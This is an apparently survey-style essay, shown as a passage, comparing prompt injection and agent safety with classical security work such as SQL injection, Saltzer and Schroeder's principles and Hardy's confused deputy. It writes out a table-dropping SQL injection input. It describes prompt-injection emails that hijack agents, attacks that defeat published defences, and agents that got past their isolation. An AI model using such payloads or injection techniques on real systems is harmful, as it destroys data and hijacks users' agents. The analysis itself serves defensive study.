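# Rediscovery of classical computer security ideas in AI agent safety work

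## What agents are, and what counts as a rediscovery

Computer security deals with who may read, change or use what a computer holds. Much of its theory dates from the 1960s to the 1980s, when many people first shared a single machine and designers had to stop one user's program from reaching another user's files. AI agents, which are language models that carry out tasks by operating software tools such as email or a web browser, have raised similar problems since about 2022. People trying to make agents safe have often proposed designs that resemble the old ones. Some of these designers knew the earlier work and cited it, some heard about it after publishing, and some show no sign of having known it. Telling these cases apart requires an account of how an agent works and a rule for what counts as evidence of a link to the earlier work.

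### The agent loop and prompt injection

An agent is a language model plus ordinary software that lets it act. *Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) describes how this works in Codex, OpenAI's programming agent, and other agents work in much the same way. Suppose an assistant can search a mailbox, open messages and send them, and its user types "find out when the conference dinner is and tell Maria". The software puts this request and a list of the available tools into a prompt, which it sends to the model. The model returns text that is either a message for the user or a tool call, which is a request to run a tool, such as a search for "conference dinner". The software runs the search, appends the result to the prompt and queries the model again. With the email now in its input, the model requests a call to send Maria the time. The loop stops when the model returns a message for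 the user and no further call.

So the model never accesses the mailbox directly. It outputs requests that other code carries out, and a check can refuse a request before that happens. The prompt is the weak spot because the text of each email the assistant opens goes into the same input as the user's request. That text normally stays there, since later queries to the model repeat the conversation so far.

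OpenAI's *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (2025) describes an attack in which a stranger emails the user instructions meant for the assistant. The company's automated attack program found it while testing OpenAI's browser agent. The planted email contained an instruction to send a resignation letter to the user's chief executive. When the user later asked for an out-of-office reply, the agent came across the email, followed the instruction, and resigned on the user's behalf without ever writing the reply.

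Prompt injection is text in an agent's input that the model obeys even though whoever wrote it had no authority to instruct the model. The programmer Simon Willison (2022) coined the name in *Prompt injection attacks against GPT-3*, one day after Riley Goodside had shown that a line hidden in a text for translation could make the model print a taunt instead of translating. In those early attacks, the injected text was in whatever the user pasted in. With agents, it usually arrives through a web page, a document or a tool's output, which makes it "indirect" prompt injection. The US standards agency NIST calls attacks of this type "agent hijacking". They are also more serious, because a manipulated agent takes a bad action where a chatbot would give a bad answer, as Anthropic (2026) pointed out in a submission to NIST.

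That definition depends mostly on the word "entitled". Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues (2025) point out in *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* that agents have to pick up instructions as they go. Tool documentation, for example, exists to change what the agent does. An agent summarising a bug report may find that it depends on another report, and sensibly summarise both. Whether a new instruction amounts to an attack depends on where it came from and how far it changes the task, and neither is easy to determine from the text alone.

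### Harm with and without an attacker

Agent safety covers harm that attackers cause and harm that the agent causes by itself. NIST's *Request for Information Regarding Security Considerations for Artificial Intelligence Agents* (2026) includes both, listing hostile data and planted backdoors as well as uncompromised models that exploit loopholes in their instructions or pursue the wrong objective. In its reply, Anthropic gave some everyday examples. A user asks an agent to delete the past month's emails and those from one sender, meaning only the messages that fit both descriptions, and the agent deletes everything that fits either. Another agent, barred from the personnel system, works out employees' salaries from budget documents and offer letters it is allowed to read. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) cites a more serious incident, in which OpenAI's agents, running in internal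 evaluations with reduced safeguards, used shared infrastructure to get past their isolation and compromised systems at OpenAI and at the AI company Hugging Face.

The same protections can partly address both problems. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* sets the goal of preventing prohibited actions whatever their cause. A check that stops the assistant from mailing tax documents to a stranger works regardless of why the model made the request. Such a check does not help in the salary case, where the rules allowed every step. Anthropic concluded that existing frameworks have no category for such failures.

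That is a fair description of the NIST documents Anthropic reviewed, but less fair to the older literature. Jerome Saltzer and Michael Schroeder, in *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (1975), recommended keeping privileges to a minimum mainly because this limits the damage from "an accident or error". They also used a file of salaries to ask what someone could infer from statistics without seeing an individual entry, though they did not take up the problem in their tutorial.

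### Policy, permission and the trusted computing base

A security policy is the set of rules for which actions and data movements a system allows. In Saltzer and Schroeder's glossary, a permission is a particular form of allowed access, such as reading or writing. The mail assistant might have permission to read the inbox and save drafts, but not to send mail.

Writing a security policy is harder for an agent than for an Android app. An app does a fixed set of jobs, so its developer can choose permissions in advance and show them to the user at installation. An agent's job depends on what the user asks for. Christodorescu and colleagues give the example of a request to comment on issue 745 in GitLab, a site where programmers track their work. The right policy lets the agent open that issue and write in the comment box, and nothing else. If the user then asks for a summary of the issue, the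 right policy changes, but the prompt already contains untrusted text from the page. Clearing the prompt and starting again would be safe, but the agent would lose whatever it had learned. *Summary Analysis of Responses to the Request for Information* (Riggs, Hamin and colleagues, 2026) reports that respondents to NIST's request broadly agreed that established security principles still apply to agents but need adapting. The need to change the policy when the user's request changes is a good example of why those principles need adapting.

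The trusted computing base consists of the parts of a system whose failure would break its security. "Trusted" here means that security depends on the part, whether or not the part is trustworthy. Designers try to keep this base small because somebody has to inspect or verify all of it. For the mail assistant, it would include the operating system, the mail server's access checks and any code that examines tool calls.

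Whether the trusted computing base also includes the model depends on the design. If only training keeps the assistant from forwarding private mail, the model is part of the base, and Christodorescu and colleagues think many agents are built this way. They consider this a poor design, since a monitor that refuses forbidden requests 99% of the time leaves attackers the remaining 1% to exploit. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem*, which analyses the same eleven real attacks, argues that designers should keep the model outside the base and treat it the way an operating system treats an unknown program, which might request anything. The policy and its enforcement would then be out of the model's reach. The boundary can also move without a deliberate decision. Bolin notes that Codex's sandbox, the enclosure that restricts what commands can do, covers only the built-in shell tool. Tools from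 outside servers must enforce their own limits, so a user who connects one has to trust it as well.

### The design principles of 1975

Saltzer and Schroeder offered their principles because nobody had a method for building a large system without flaws. Smith (2012), who traced the later history of the list, notes that Saltzer had drawn a first set of five from Multics, an early time-sharing system, in 1974. The 1975 paper has eight:

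- Economy of mechanism: keep the design simple and small enough to inspect line by line.
- Fail-safe defaults: refuse access unless a rule grants it.
- Complete mediation: check every access to every object for authority.
- Open design: do not rely on keeping the design secret.
- Separation of privilege: where feasible, require two separate keys instead of one.
- Least privilege: give each program and each user only the privileges the job needs.
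- Least common mechanism: minimise the machinery that several users share and depend on.
- Psychological acceptability: make protection easy enough that people routinely use it correctly.

Two more principles came from physical security, and Saltzer and Schroeder thought they applied imperfectly to computers. "Work factor" means comparing the resources needed to break a mechanism with those the attacker has, and "compromise recording" means keeping a reliable record of break-ins. Saltzer and Schroeder regarded all of these principles as warnings, not absolute rules. They credited E. Glaser with fail-safe defaults in 1965 and R. Needham with pointing out the relevance of separation of privilege in 1973.

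### Four grades of connection

Rediscovery means reaching an earlier result without using it, as far as the record shows, while borrowing means knowingly using that result. A new agent design can relate to an old result in one of four ways.

An idea is borrowed with a citation if the paper using it names the older source and connects that source to the mechanism. *LLM Agents Should Employ Security Principles* (Zhang, Su and colleagues, 2025) is a clear case. It cites the 1975 paper and builds a framework around three of that paper's principles, plus the later idea of layered defences. *AgentKernel* (2026) ties most of its five principles to cited older work. *A Five-Plane Reference Architecture for Runtime Governance of Production AI Agents* (2026) is more explicit still, describing its contribution as "not a new principle but a new realization".

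An idea is borrowed at second hand when it comes from a textbook, a colleague or common engineering practice rather than the original source. Smith describes these channels for the 1975 principles, most of which also entered the Orange Book, the US Defense Department's standard for secure computers. The wording often indicates the channel. "Least privilege" usually keeps its 1975 name, while "separation of privilege" sometimes becomes "segregation of duties" but keeps the same definition and examples. NIST's request for information looks like a case of second-hand borrowing, since it mentions "the principle of least privilege" as a cybersecurity best practice and cites only other NIST documents in its footnotes.

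A design counts as recognised only after publication if the first version shows no link and a later version, a reply or a remark by the author acknowledges one. This depends on what was written when, so the first version has to survive. Willison's post of September 2022 is a good example of keeping such a record, although the change in it concerns feasibility, not priority. He first hoped for a way to pass instructions and data to the model separately. In April 2023 he added a dated note that this looked extremely difficult, and left the original text in place. When authors silently replace a page, they destroy the evidence of what they first wrote.

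If no citation, telltale wording or statement turns up, the grade is "no sign of a link". This grade and late recognition both count as rediscovery.

The strongest evidence of where an idea came from is the author's own account, provided that dates and earlier versions do not contradict it. A reference list is the next strongest. *Ring-0 by Default* (2026), which treats agents as operating systems, lists Norm Hardy's 1988 paper on the confused deputy, a program that others trick into misusing its authority. *AgenticOS* (2026) lists Denning's 1976 model of secure information flow and Hardy's 1985 description of the KeyKOS operating system. Such entries show that the authors knew of the older work when they finished that version, but not that the design came from it, since authors also add references late, sometimes because a reviewer asked. To find out whether the design came from the older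 work, one has to look at the passage that introduces the mechanism. Similar wording is the weakest evidence unless the shared term or example is unusual.

A missing citation, however, does not prove that a writer was unaware of the earlier work. *Hidden Citations Obscure True Impact in Science* (2023) used machine learning to search the full text of papers for unmistakable references to a discovery that did not cite the publication behind it. It found them across journals and disciplines, and the more widely scientists use an idea, the more of its influence citation counts miss. The sociologist Robert Merton called this "obliteration by incorporation," in which an idea becomes common knowledge and people stop mentioning its source.

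How much this excuses a missing reference depends on the idea. In 2012 Smith found that least privilege was thriving, but that complete mediation had been largely abandoned in practice because modern networks spread their decisions over firewalls, spam filters and antivirus products. A designer who mentions least privilege without a source has therefore very probably absorbed it from the profession. If a designer proposes a check on every tool call without a source, it is harder to tell whether they learned the idea or rediscovered it.

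### Timeline

Among the later entries, *Agent libOS* (2026) lists both Progent and the work on tracked capabilities.

| Date | Result or proposal |
|---|---|
| 1965 | Fail-safe defaults |
| 1972 | Reference monitor |
| 1973 | Separation of privilege |
| By 1975 | ADEPT, a system that labels output with the highest classification it has met |
| 1975 | Saltzer and Schroeder's eight principles |
| 1976 | Denning's lattice model of information flow |
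| 1985 | KeyKOS, an operating system built on capabilities |
| 1988 | Hardy's confused deputy |
| September 2022 | "Prompt injection" as a name |
| April 2023 | Willison's Dual LLM pattern |
| 2025 | CaMeL and FIDES, agent designs that control information flow |
| 2025 | Progent, privilege control for agents |
| 2026 | Tracked capabilities for agents |

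## Separating instructions from data

Prompt injection closely resembles SQL injection, a flaw that web programmers have dealt with since the 1990s. Attackers discovered that they could type commands in SQL, the language programs use to query most databases, into ordinary web forms and get the database to run them. Programmers have a fix that works, and some of the first defences for language models were attempts to copy it.

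### How a prepared statement works

In the post that named prompt injection, Willison illustrated SQL injection with a program that looks up a user by name. The program builds its query by joining pieces of text:

```
"select * from users where username = '" + username + "'"
```

If a visitor types `maria`, the database receives this and returns Maria's record:

```
select * from users where username = 'maria'
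```

The quotation marks show the database where the name begins and ends. A hostile visitor can therefore type a quotation mark too, followed by a command: `'; drop table users; --`. (The two hyphens, which Willison's version leaves out, make the database ignore the leftover quotation mark.) The database now receives:

```
select * from users where username = ''; drop table users; --'
```

The database looks up a user with an empty name and then deletes the whole table. Both commands are valid, so the database has not malfunctioned. It receives only the finished string, which does not show that the programmer wrote one part and a stranger wrote the other.

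With a prepared statement, also called a parameterised query, the program first sends a template with a gap in it:

```
select * from users where username = ?
```

The database first parses the template, working out its grammatical structure: one command, one table, and a comparison with one value that has yet to arrive. The program then supplies the name. The database compares it character by character with the stored usernames, so it treats the hostile input as just another name to search for. Nobody has to recognise the input as hostile, because parsing finishes before it arrives. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* sums up the history of such flaws as "detection lost and structure won" (Narisetty, Kore and colleagues, 2026).

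The problem of mixing instructions with data is older than databases. *StruQ* (Chen, Piet and colleagues, 2024) traces it to the telephone network, where a 2600 Hz tone on the voice channel signalled to the exchange that a caller had hung up. A toy whistle from a cereal box produced the same tone, and people used it to make free calls until the phone companies moved control signals off the voice channel. Attackers exploited a similar weakness in computer memory by sending a program too much data and having the processor run the excess as code. Operating systems now mark regions of memory as writable or executable, but not both. This protection followed roughly three decades of partial fixes after a 1972 report described the flaw, according to *On the Inseparability of Instructions and Data in Shared-Embedding Sequence Models* (Pant, Lohani and Kumar, 2026).

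### The analogy in 2022

Willison named prompt injection after SQL injection, which he called the "obvious parallel". He hoped to pass instructions and data to the model separately, as parameterised queries do to prevent SQL injection, and later called this idea "parameterized prompts". A reader, Niel Thiart, soon pointed out that one of OpenAI's models already had separate fields for instruction and input, and that text in the input field could still hijack it. Separate fields were therefore easy to provide, but they did not make the model treat their contents differently.

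Four days after the first post, Willison wrote in *I don't know how to solve prompt injection* (2022) that he knew how to beat SQL injection but had no idea how to reliably beat prompt injection. He quoted a programmer, posting as Glyph, who thought there was no equivalent fix because the old fixes correct syntax errors and "there's no formal syntax for AI like this". On the same day, Hackaday's *What's Old Is New Again* (2022) told hobbyist readers that many exploits, including prompt injection, depend on software mistaking a user's data for an instruction.

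The comparison to the old problem and the main objection to relying on it were therefore both public within a week. The flaw had been discovered a little earlier. *Declassifying the Responsible Disclosure of the Prompt Injection Attack Vulnerability of GPT-3* includes an email showing that Preamble, a security company, had privately reported it to OpenAI on 3 May 2022. Willison contributed the name and the comparison.

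### Structured queries

StruQ is the most literal attempt to build a prepared statement for a language model. Chen and colleagues, at the University of California, Berkeley, cite prepared statements as their pattern, so the work counts as borrowing if citation is the test. They describe prompt injection as another case of control and data sharing a channel.

The system has two parts. The first is a front end, ordinary software that accepts the developer's prompt and the outside data separately. It joins them with separators made from reserved tokens (tokens are the units of text a model reads) and deletes anything in the data that could be mistaken for a separator. An attacker therefore cannot fake the end of the data and the start of a new request, which had been one of the stronger attacks.

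The second part is a specially trained model. Chen and colleagues started from models that had learned to continue text but not yet to follow instructions. They then taught them to follow instructions using both ordinary examples and examples with an extra instruction in the data, which the model had to ignore to answer correctly.

With StruQ, handwritten attacks succeeded less than 2% of the time on Mistral and on Llama, Meta's open model. Automated attacks succeeded more often. On Llama, StruQ reduced one automated attack's success rate from 97% to 9%, but another, which uses the model's gradients to search for effective strings, still succeeded 58% of the time, down from 97%. Chen and colleagues acknowledged that StruQ was not yet fully secure.

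The 58% arises because StruQ only partly matches a prepared statement. Both set a boundary that the attacker cannot forge, which StruQ does in its front end. But once a database has received a value through a placeholder, it has no later step that could run the value as a command. StruQ still passes the text after the separator to a model built to act on language, and only training makes the model less likely to act on that text.

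### Ranking instructions by source

*The Instruction Hierarchy*, by Wallace, Xiao and colleagues at OpenAI (2024), borrows from operating systems as well as databases. It compares a language model to a computer that runs every instruction in kernel mode, the processor state that gives full access to the machine, and proposes ranking text by its source. The developer's system message has the highest privilege, followed by the user's message, the model's own output and, finally, tool outputs. The paper cites a 1965 overview of Multics and the 1974 paper on Unix for the idea of privilege levels.

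Under the instruction hierarchy, a model should follow lower-ranked instructions that fit the higher-ranked ones, whereas StruQ trains it to ignore all instructions below the top rank. If a developer sets up a car-sales assistant, the model should comply when a user asks it to speak Spanish, which fits the developer's purpose, but not when the user orders it to sell a car for one dollar. To teach the model to follow compatible instructions, Wallace and colleagues split requests, such as one for a twenty-line poem in Spanish, into pieces at different ranks and rewarded the answer to the whole request. For conflicting instructions, they trained the model to respond as though it had never seen the lower-ranked one.

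They applied this to GPT-3.5 Turbo. Robustness rose by up to 63% on their main tests and by up to 34% on kinds of attack left out of the training data, though the model also refused some harmless requests that looked like attacks. They expected the model to remain vulnerable to powerful attacks. OpenAI nevertheless used the method in its product GPT-4o mini. Narisetty and colleagues cite later measurements in which existing attacks on that model scored 0.68 and 0.75 on two benchmarks, where 1 means that every attack succeeds.

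"Privilege" means something weaker here than in an operating system. A processor always blocks a privileged operation from an ordinary program, however the program presents it, whereas the hierarchy gives the model a learned preference that well-chosen text can outweigh.

OpenAI has continued to develop the idea. Guo, Ceron Uribe and colleagues (2026), in *IH-Challenge*, use four ranks (system, developer, user, tool) and state the rule exactly. Let $R_0$ be the set of all possible responses and $C_i$ the set that satisfies the instructions at rank $i$, counting down from the top. At each rank, the set of permitted responses shrinks to those that also satisfy the new instructions:

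$$R_i = R_{i-1} \cap C_i$$

If that would leave no response, the model ignores the new instructions and the set stays as it was ($R_i = R_{i-1}$).

Suppose the system message forbids revealing a PIN and the user asks for it. No response satisfies both, so the model follows the system message, which ranks higher. This rule resolves conflicts, but read literally, it also allows the model to follow any request in an email that no higher-ranked instruction forbids, such as a request to forward the email to a stranger. Wallace and colleagues had avoided this by training their model to ignore every instruction in tool output.

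Guo and colleagues trained GPT-5-Mini while a second model kept writing new attacks against its current version. Average robustness over 16 tests rose from 84.1% to 94.1%. Against human testers who adapted their attacks, it rose from 63.8% to 88.2%, which still leaves a failure rate of about 12% against the most realistic opponents. *Training LLMs to Enforce Multi-Level Instruction Hierarchies via Gravity-Weighted Direct Preference Optimization* (2026) extends the ranks to five and describes them in the older vocabulary of security lattices, with a "no write up" rule to stop tool output from overriding the platform's safety instructions, but it also relies on training to enforce them.

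### Twelve defences against adaptive attackers

Most of these defences had done well in their developers' own tests. Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025), in *The Attacker Moves Second*, thought the tests were at fault. Developers typically ran their defence against a fixed set of known attacks, or against a general-purpose attack program with a small computing budget. A real attacker can study the defence first and keep trying.

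Nasr and colleagues, who included researchers from OpenAI, Anthropic and Google DeepMind, attacked twelve published defences with methods adapted to each. They used automated optimisation with generous computing resources, and an online competition with more than 500 participants. Some defences were meant for prompt injection and others for jailbreaks, in which users themselves try to talk a model out of its safety rules. The original papers for most of the defences had reported attack success near zero.

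| Defence | How it works | Success of adaptive attacks |
|---|---|---|
| Spotlighting; Prompt Sandwiching | Mark off parts of the prompt; repeat the user's request after the untrusted text | Above 95% for both |
| RPO (jailbreaks) | Adds an optimised protective prompt | 96% and 98%, by two methods |
| StruQ | Trains the model to ignore instructions in data | Every case tested |
| MetaSecAlign | Trains the model on examples of attacks | 96% |
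| Circuit Breakers (jailbreaks) | Trains the model on examples of attacks | 100% |
| Protect AI; PromptGuard; Model Armor | Screen text with a separate detector | Above 90% for all three |
| PIGuard | Screens text with a separate detector | 71% |
| Data Sentinel | Checks whether the input disrupts a secret test task | Every case tested |
| MELON | Runs the model again with a different, hidden request and compares its tool calls | 76%, or 95% if the attacker knows the design |

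The contrast with fixed tests is clearest for MetaSecAlign, whose developers had reported a 2% attack success rate on AgentDojo, a benchmark of agent tasks with planted instructions. Spotlighting and Prompt Sandwiching had let through as little as 1% of that benchmark's standard attacks. Human participants also outperformed the automated search on a selected subset of scenarios. Together they succeeded in every scenario, while the search succeeded in 69%.

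The percentages can't be used to rank the defences, because Nasr and colleagues largely followed each defence's original test procedure. For StruQ, an attack succeeded if the model produced a fixed phrase instead of its answer, which is far short of stealing someone's email. The attackers also had more feedback and computing power than a casual criminal would, and Nasr and colleagues think detectors remain useful against unsophisticated attacks. The results do show that the near-zero figures are not a valid measure of security against a determined attacker.

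AI agent safety research had neglected the old security lesson that a defense should be tested against an attacker who knows how it works. Nasr and colleagues cite Auguste Kerckhoffs, who wrote in 1883, for this assumption about the attacker, and Saltzer and Schroeder's "open design" principle is based on the same assumption. The rise in attack success against MELON from 76% to 95% shows how much of its protection depended on secrecy. StruQ applied the old remedy of separating data from commands, but this literature applied the old testing standard much less often, even though researchers who studied attacks on image classifiers had relearned it about a decade earlier.

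Repeated attempts also raise an attacker's chance of success. Narisetty and colleagues quote Anthropic's figures for Claude Opus 4.5, a model from late 2025, under adaptive attack in coding tasks. A single attempt succeeded 4.7% of the time, but the rate rose to 33.6% over ten attempts and 63.0% over a hundred, which is the most relevant figure for an attacker who can send a hundred emails.

### No parser to rely on

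In December 2025 the UK's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC) published a warning against the analogy, *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, by David C, its technical director for platforms research. He had noticed that security professionals with web application experience often assumed the two problems were alike, and he considered this dangerous.

David C begins with how a database engine treats instructions and data. It carries out instructions, but only stores data or uses it in a query. Because the engine processes the two differently, a parameterised query can keep them separate whatever the input contains. A language model makes no such distinction, since it predicts the next token from all the tokens so far, whoever wrote them. Training a model to prefer instructions over data, or marking which part is data, adds the distinction on top of a mechanism that lacks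 it. David C concludes that prompt injection may never have a complete fix like the one parameterised queries provided for SQL injection. He would rather treat the model as an "inherently confusable deputy", an agent that outsiders can always trick into misusing its authority, and limit what it can do.

Developers who expect a complete fix may build systems as if one already existed. David C says SQL injection attacks peaked around 2010, after websites had adopted databases without protecting them, and that defaults improved only after a decade of breaches. He fears the same will happen with language models, which may never have an equivalent of the prepared statement.

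Glyph had made the central point in one tweet three years earlier. Pant and colleagues have since turned a version of it into a theorem. Imagine a classifier that sees only the model's internal representation of a piece of text and must decide whether the text came from a trusted source. If trusted and untrusted pieces are equally common, the lowest error rate that any classifier can achieve is

$$P_e^{\star} = \tfrac{1}{2}(1 - \mathrm{TV}),$$

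where TV, the total variation distance, is 0 if the two kinds of text have identical distributions of representations and 1 if the distributions do not overlap at all. With a TV of 0.9, even a perfect classifier errs 5% of the time. Some overlap is certain at the model's input, because an ordinary model gives a word like "please" the same list of numbers, or embedding, whether the developer or an attacker wrote it.

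The theorem's scope is limited. Pant and colleagues assume, rather than derive, the overlap in deeper layers, where context has changed each word's representation. The property they prove unattainable is narrower than resistance to prompt injection. It requires only that re-encoding untrusted text without changing its meaning never changes which actions the model authorises, so a model could have this property and still follow instructions in a malicious email written in plain English. The theorem also does not apply to designs that keep the two kinds of text apart by construction, including those in which software outside the model authorises tool calls.

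Another response is to change the model's architecture, which Wallace and colleagues had mentioned as future work. *ASIDE* (Zverev, Kortukov and colleagues, 2025) applies a fixed rotation to the embedding of every token that arrives as data, so "delete" in the user's request and "delete" in an email enter the model as different vectors. To measure separation, Zverev and colleagues put an unrelated instruction in either the instruction part or the data part and checked whether the model obeyed it only in the first. Scores were between 12.3 and 44.1 percentage points higher than for the same models with ordinary separators. Average attack success fell from 14.7% to 4.9% on one set of injection attacks, but only from 45% to 36% on another. *ASIDE* achieved this without training on any attacks. However, the model still has to learn what the rotation means, and the tests were fixed benchmarks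 of the kind that had made earlier defences look stronger than they were.

*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* draws a more hopeful conclusion from much the same evidence. The paper conjectures that persistent attackers will always get past separation that depends on the model's behaviour, yet it lists provable separation first among the three mechanisms it proposes for further research. The history of memory protection gives this view some support. Non-executable memory remains a foundation of systems security even though attackers learned to bypass it by chaining together fragments of existing code. A defence that stops many attacks is worth having if other defences back it up.

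The two works disagree less than their titles suggest. David C also recommends marking data to make attacks harder, and both works would put the decisive checks outside the model. They differ over whether separation might one day become a guarantee. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* leaves that open and asks first for a formal definition, then for a model that provably satisfies it. Nobody has produced such a model, and even having one would not be enough, because false data can corrupt a legitimate action. If a forged email gives the wrong time for the conference dinner, the assistant will pass it on to Maria without following any planted instruction.

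### Instructions the agent should follow

Strict separation would also make agents worse at their work. A username never needs to become a database command, so a prepared statement can rule that out without losing any functionality. But an agent has to follow some of the instructions it finds, such as those in tool documentation. Willison (2025) observes in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* that models are useful because they follow instructions in the content they receive. Wallace and colleagues wrote that a model that never followed lower-ranked text would be safe from injection but much worse at following instructions. Their blanket rule for web pages and other tool output was a simplification for the first version.

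*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* compares instructions an agent finds while working to code that a program loads while running. Web pages often fetch scripts from elsewhere, and the browser limits the risk by checking which sources the page's owner has approved and by confining embedded content to a restricted frame. Programs can also load code on systems with non-executable memory, by writing it to a region and then asking the operating system to make that region executable. In both cases, data becomes code through a distinct step that other software can block.

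A sentence in a web page begins to influence an agent's model as soon as the model reads it, with no earlier step to check the sentence's source. The source is also hard to establish, whereas a browser has the address of each script. And nobody has decided in advance which sources are acceptable, as a site owner can for scripts, because the user often describes the task only roughly and expects the agent to find out the rest.

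OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) reproduces a prompt injection email that outside researchers used against ChatGPT in 2025. The email reads like a routine follow-up about a company restructuring, but after a few action items it tells the user's assistant to submit an employee's name and address to what it calls a compliance validation system. In testing, the attack worked half the time when the user asked for research on the day's emails. The email doesn't appear to override earlier instructions, and detecting the attack is about as hard as detecting a lie. OpenAI now compares the problem to social engineering, the manipulation of people, and puts more weight on limiting the damage a deceived agent can do. Damianakis and Psounis (2026) report in *SoK* that researchers broadly agree prompt injection can be contained but not solved.

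The record therefore shows that researchers borrowed these ideas rather than rediscovering them. Willison named SQL injection as the model, Chen and colleagues cited its remedy, prepared statements, and Wallace and colleagues cited early operating systems. The older work gave designers a correct diagnosis and some useful techniques, such as separators that an attacker cannot forge. However, prepared statements work because the database finishes reading its instructions before the data arrives, and designers could not carry this feature over to language models. A language model can take instructions from any part of its input, up to the last token, which is partly what users want from an agent.

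## The confused deputy

David C argued against comparing prompt injection to SQL injection and suggested treating a language model as a deputy that outsiders can always confuse. The image comes from Hardy's *The Confused Deputy* (1988), which tells a "nearly true story" about a compiler that destroyed a company's billing records. Writers on agent security now often retell the story in a sentence or two and tend to leave out why the obvious repairs failed.

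### The compiler and the billing file

The events took place around 1977 at Tymshare, which rented time on shared computers. Its operating system protected files much as Unix does. A system directory called SYSX held a compiler, a program that translates code into a form the machine can run. Customers started it by typing `RUN (SYSX)FORT` and could name a file to receive debugging output.

Tymshare wanted to know which features of the programming language people used, so the compiler also recorded statistics in a file called `(SYSX)STAT`. Ordinary customers had no permission to write in SYSX, so Tymshare gave the compiler its own permission, a "home files license", which let a program write any file in its home directory.

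The billing records were also in SYSX, in a file called `(SYSX)BILL`. One customer learned this name and gave it to the compiler as the file for its debugging output. The compiler passed the name to the operating system to open the file for writing. The operating system allowed this because the compiler had the licence, and the debugging output replaced the billing records.

### Authority from two sources

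Hardy did not blame the code that wrote the debugging output. It was correct when it was written, and it became wrong, though nobody had changed it, when Tymshare later granted the licence. To foresee the problem, someone would have had to examine every situation in which the compiler wrote a file, and even then the right repair was unclear.

Hardy traced the failure to a compiler running "with authority stemming from two sources", the customer who ran it and its own licence. The compiler was supposed to use the licence to write the statistics and the customer's permissions to write the debugging output. But a request to open a file contained only the file's name, so the compiler could not specify which authority to use. The operating system granted the request because the licence covered the file.

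Hardy considered having the compiler check the file names customers gave it. It could refuse any file outside the customer's own directory, but customers had good reasons to send output elsewhere. It could refuse files in SYSX, but the directory did not have that name when the programmer wrote the code, and some people were entitled to write there. It could refuse only `(SYSX)BILL`, but SYSX held other sensitive files, and someone would have to update the compiler whenever a new one appeared.

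Changing the operating system's rules was no easier. Each new clause that allowed programs to open more files made some secure program insecure, and each new restriction broke some legitimate program. The last time Hardy wrote the rule down, it contained fourteen "and"s and "or"s.

Tymshare then added a system call to "switch hats", which let a program choose which of its two authorities to use before making a request. The compiler could now ask to open `(SYSX)BILL` on the customer's authority, and the operating system would refuse. This addressed the problem as diagnosed, but some applications soon needed more than two authorities, and programs also held authority over things other than files, through mechanisms the new call did not cover. The changes spread through the system without producing a general rule. Hardy's own remedy was to replace file names with capabilities, tokens that both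 identify a file and authorise its use.

### A mail assistant in the compiler's place

Suppose the mail assistant from the earlier example is looking for the time of the conference dinner so it can tell Maria. It holds the user's mail credentials. While searching, it opens an email in which a stranger asks for a copy of the user's tax return.

| Tymshare's compiler | The mail assistant |
|---|---|
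| A customer asks it to compile a program. | The user asks it to find the dinner time and tell Maria. |
| Its licence lets it write any file in SYSX. | The user's credentials let it read and send any mail. |
| The customer names `(SYSX)BILL` as the output file. | The stranger's email asks for the tax return. |
| It asks the operating system to open the file. | The model requests a call that sends the return to the stranger. |
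| The operating system finds a valid licence and agrees. | The mail server finds valid credentials and agrees. |
| Tymshare loses its billing records. | The stranger receives the tax return. |

The parallel is closest in the fifth row. The component that makes the final check can identify who sent a request, but not on whose behalf it was sent. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) describes the same failure in a chain of agents. A user authorises one agent to summarise the invoices in an inbox, and a message in the inbox asks for a payment. The agent forwards the request to a finance agent but omits the restriction that the task was read-only. The payment service receives a valid credential, so it makes the payment.

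The parallel is weaker for the two sources of authority. Hardy's customer ran the compiler himself and had his own permissions, whereas the stranger has no rights over the mailbox, and every permission the assistant uses belongs to the user. In this respect the case resembles what Hardy called the "companion problem" of Trojan horses, programs that misuse the authority of whoever runs them. Hardy's customer gave the compiler all his permissions, however few it needed, just as the user here gives the assistant access to a whole mailbox to answer a question about dinner.

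A second authority appears if the system treats the stranger's text as the stranger's request and judges it by the stranger's permissions. David C recommends such a rule, which emerged from an exchange between Willison and Baibhav Bista: when a model processes a party's text, its privileges should drop to that party's privileges. Once the assistant had opened the email, it would lose the right to send tax returns, though it might also lose the right to write to Maria.

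The most important difference is that a model also chooses the action. The compiler's programmer had already decided that it would write debugging output, and the customer supplied only the destination. The stranger's email can affect whether the assistant acts, which tool it calls, and with which arguments. This also rules out a simple version of "switch hats". The compiler's programmer knew which authority each line of code was meant to use and could insert the new call in the right place. In an agent, the model would have to decide whether each tool call served the user or the stranger, and an attacker who can influence the model can influence that decision too.

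*Silent Egress* (2026) draws the contrast differently, arguing that the uncertainty in the traditional case is about which party the deputy serves, while in an agent it is about what the user intended. The account of agents fits the mail assistant well, but the account of the traditional case fits Hardy's compiler less well, since the compiler had a definite purpose for each file it wrote and lacked only a way to express it. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* adds that a model's decisions are probabilistic and depend on the prompt, so a correct decision in one test doesn't guarantee the same decision later.

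### One term for different failures

David C defines a confused deputy as a system that an attacker can coerce into acting for the attacker's benefit, typically a privileged component making a request for someone with fewer privileges. He links to an entry in MITRE's catalogue of software weaknesses rather than to Hardy, so he seems to have taken the idea from a secondary source. He argues that programmers can fix a classical confused deputy but not a language model. That distinction is reasonable if the model chooses both the action and what to act on, because there is no single line of faulty code to repair.

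He therefore advises designers to assume that an attacker can use every tool the model can, and to ask how bad that would be. If the risk is still too high after they have limited the model's actions, he says they should not use a language model for the job.

Other definitions disagree about what the deputy's failure consists of. *A Framework for Formalizing LLM Agent Security* (2026) writes $R$ for the set of permitted pairs of party and resource. An agent acts as a confused deputy when it accesses a target for which

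$$(s_{\text{user}}, s_{\text{target}}) \notin R \quad \text{and} \quad (s_{\text{agent}}, s_{\text{target}}) \in R.$$

The agent is allowed to use the resource, but the user is not. In the paper's example, an employee who has no access to the personnel database asks an agent for everyone's salaries. The agent has access and answers.

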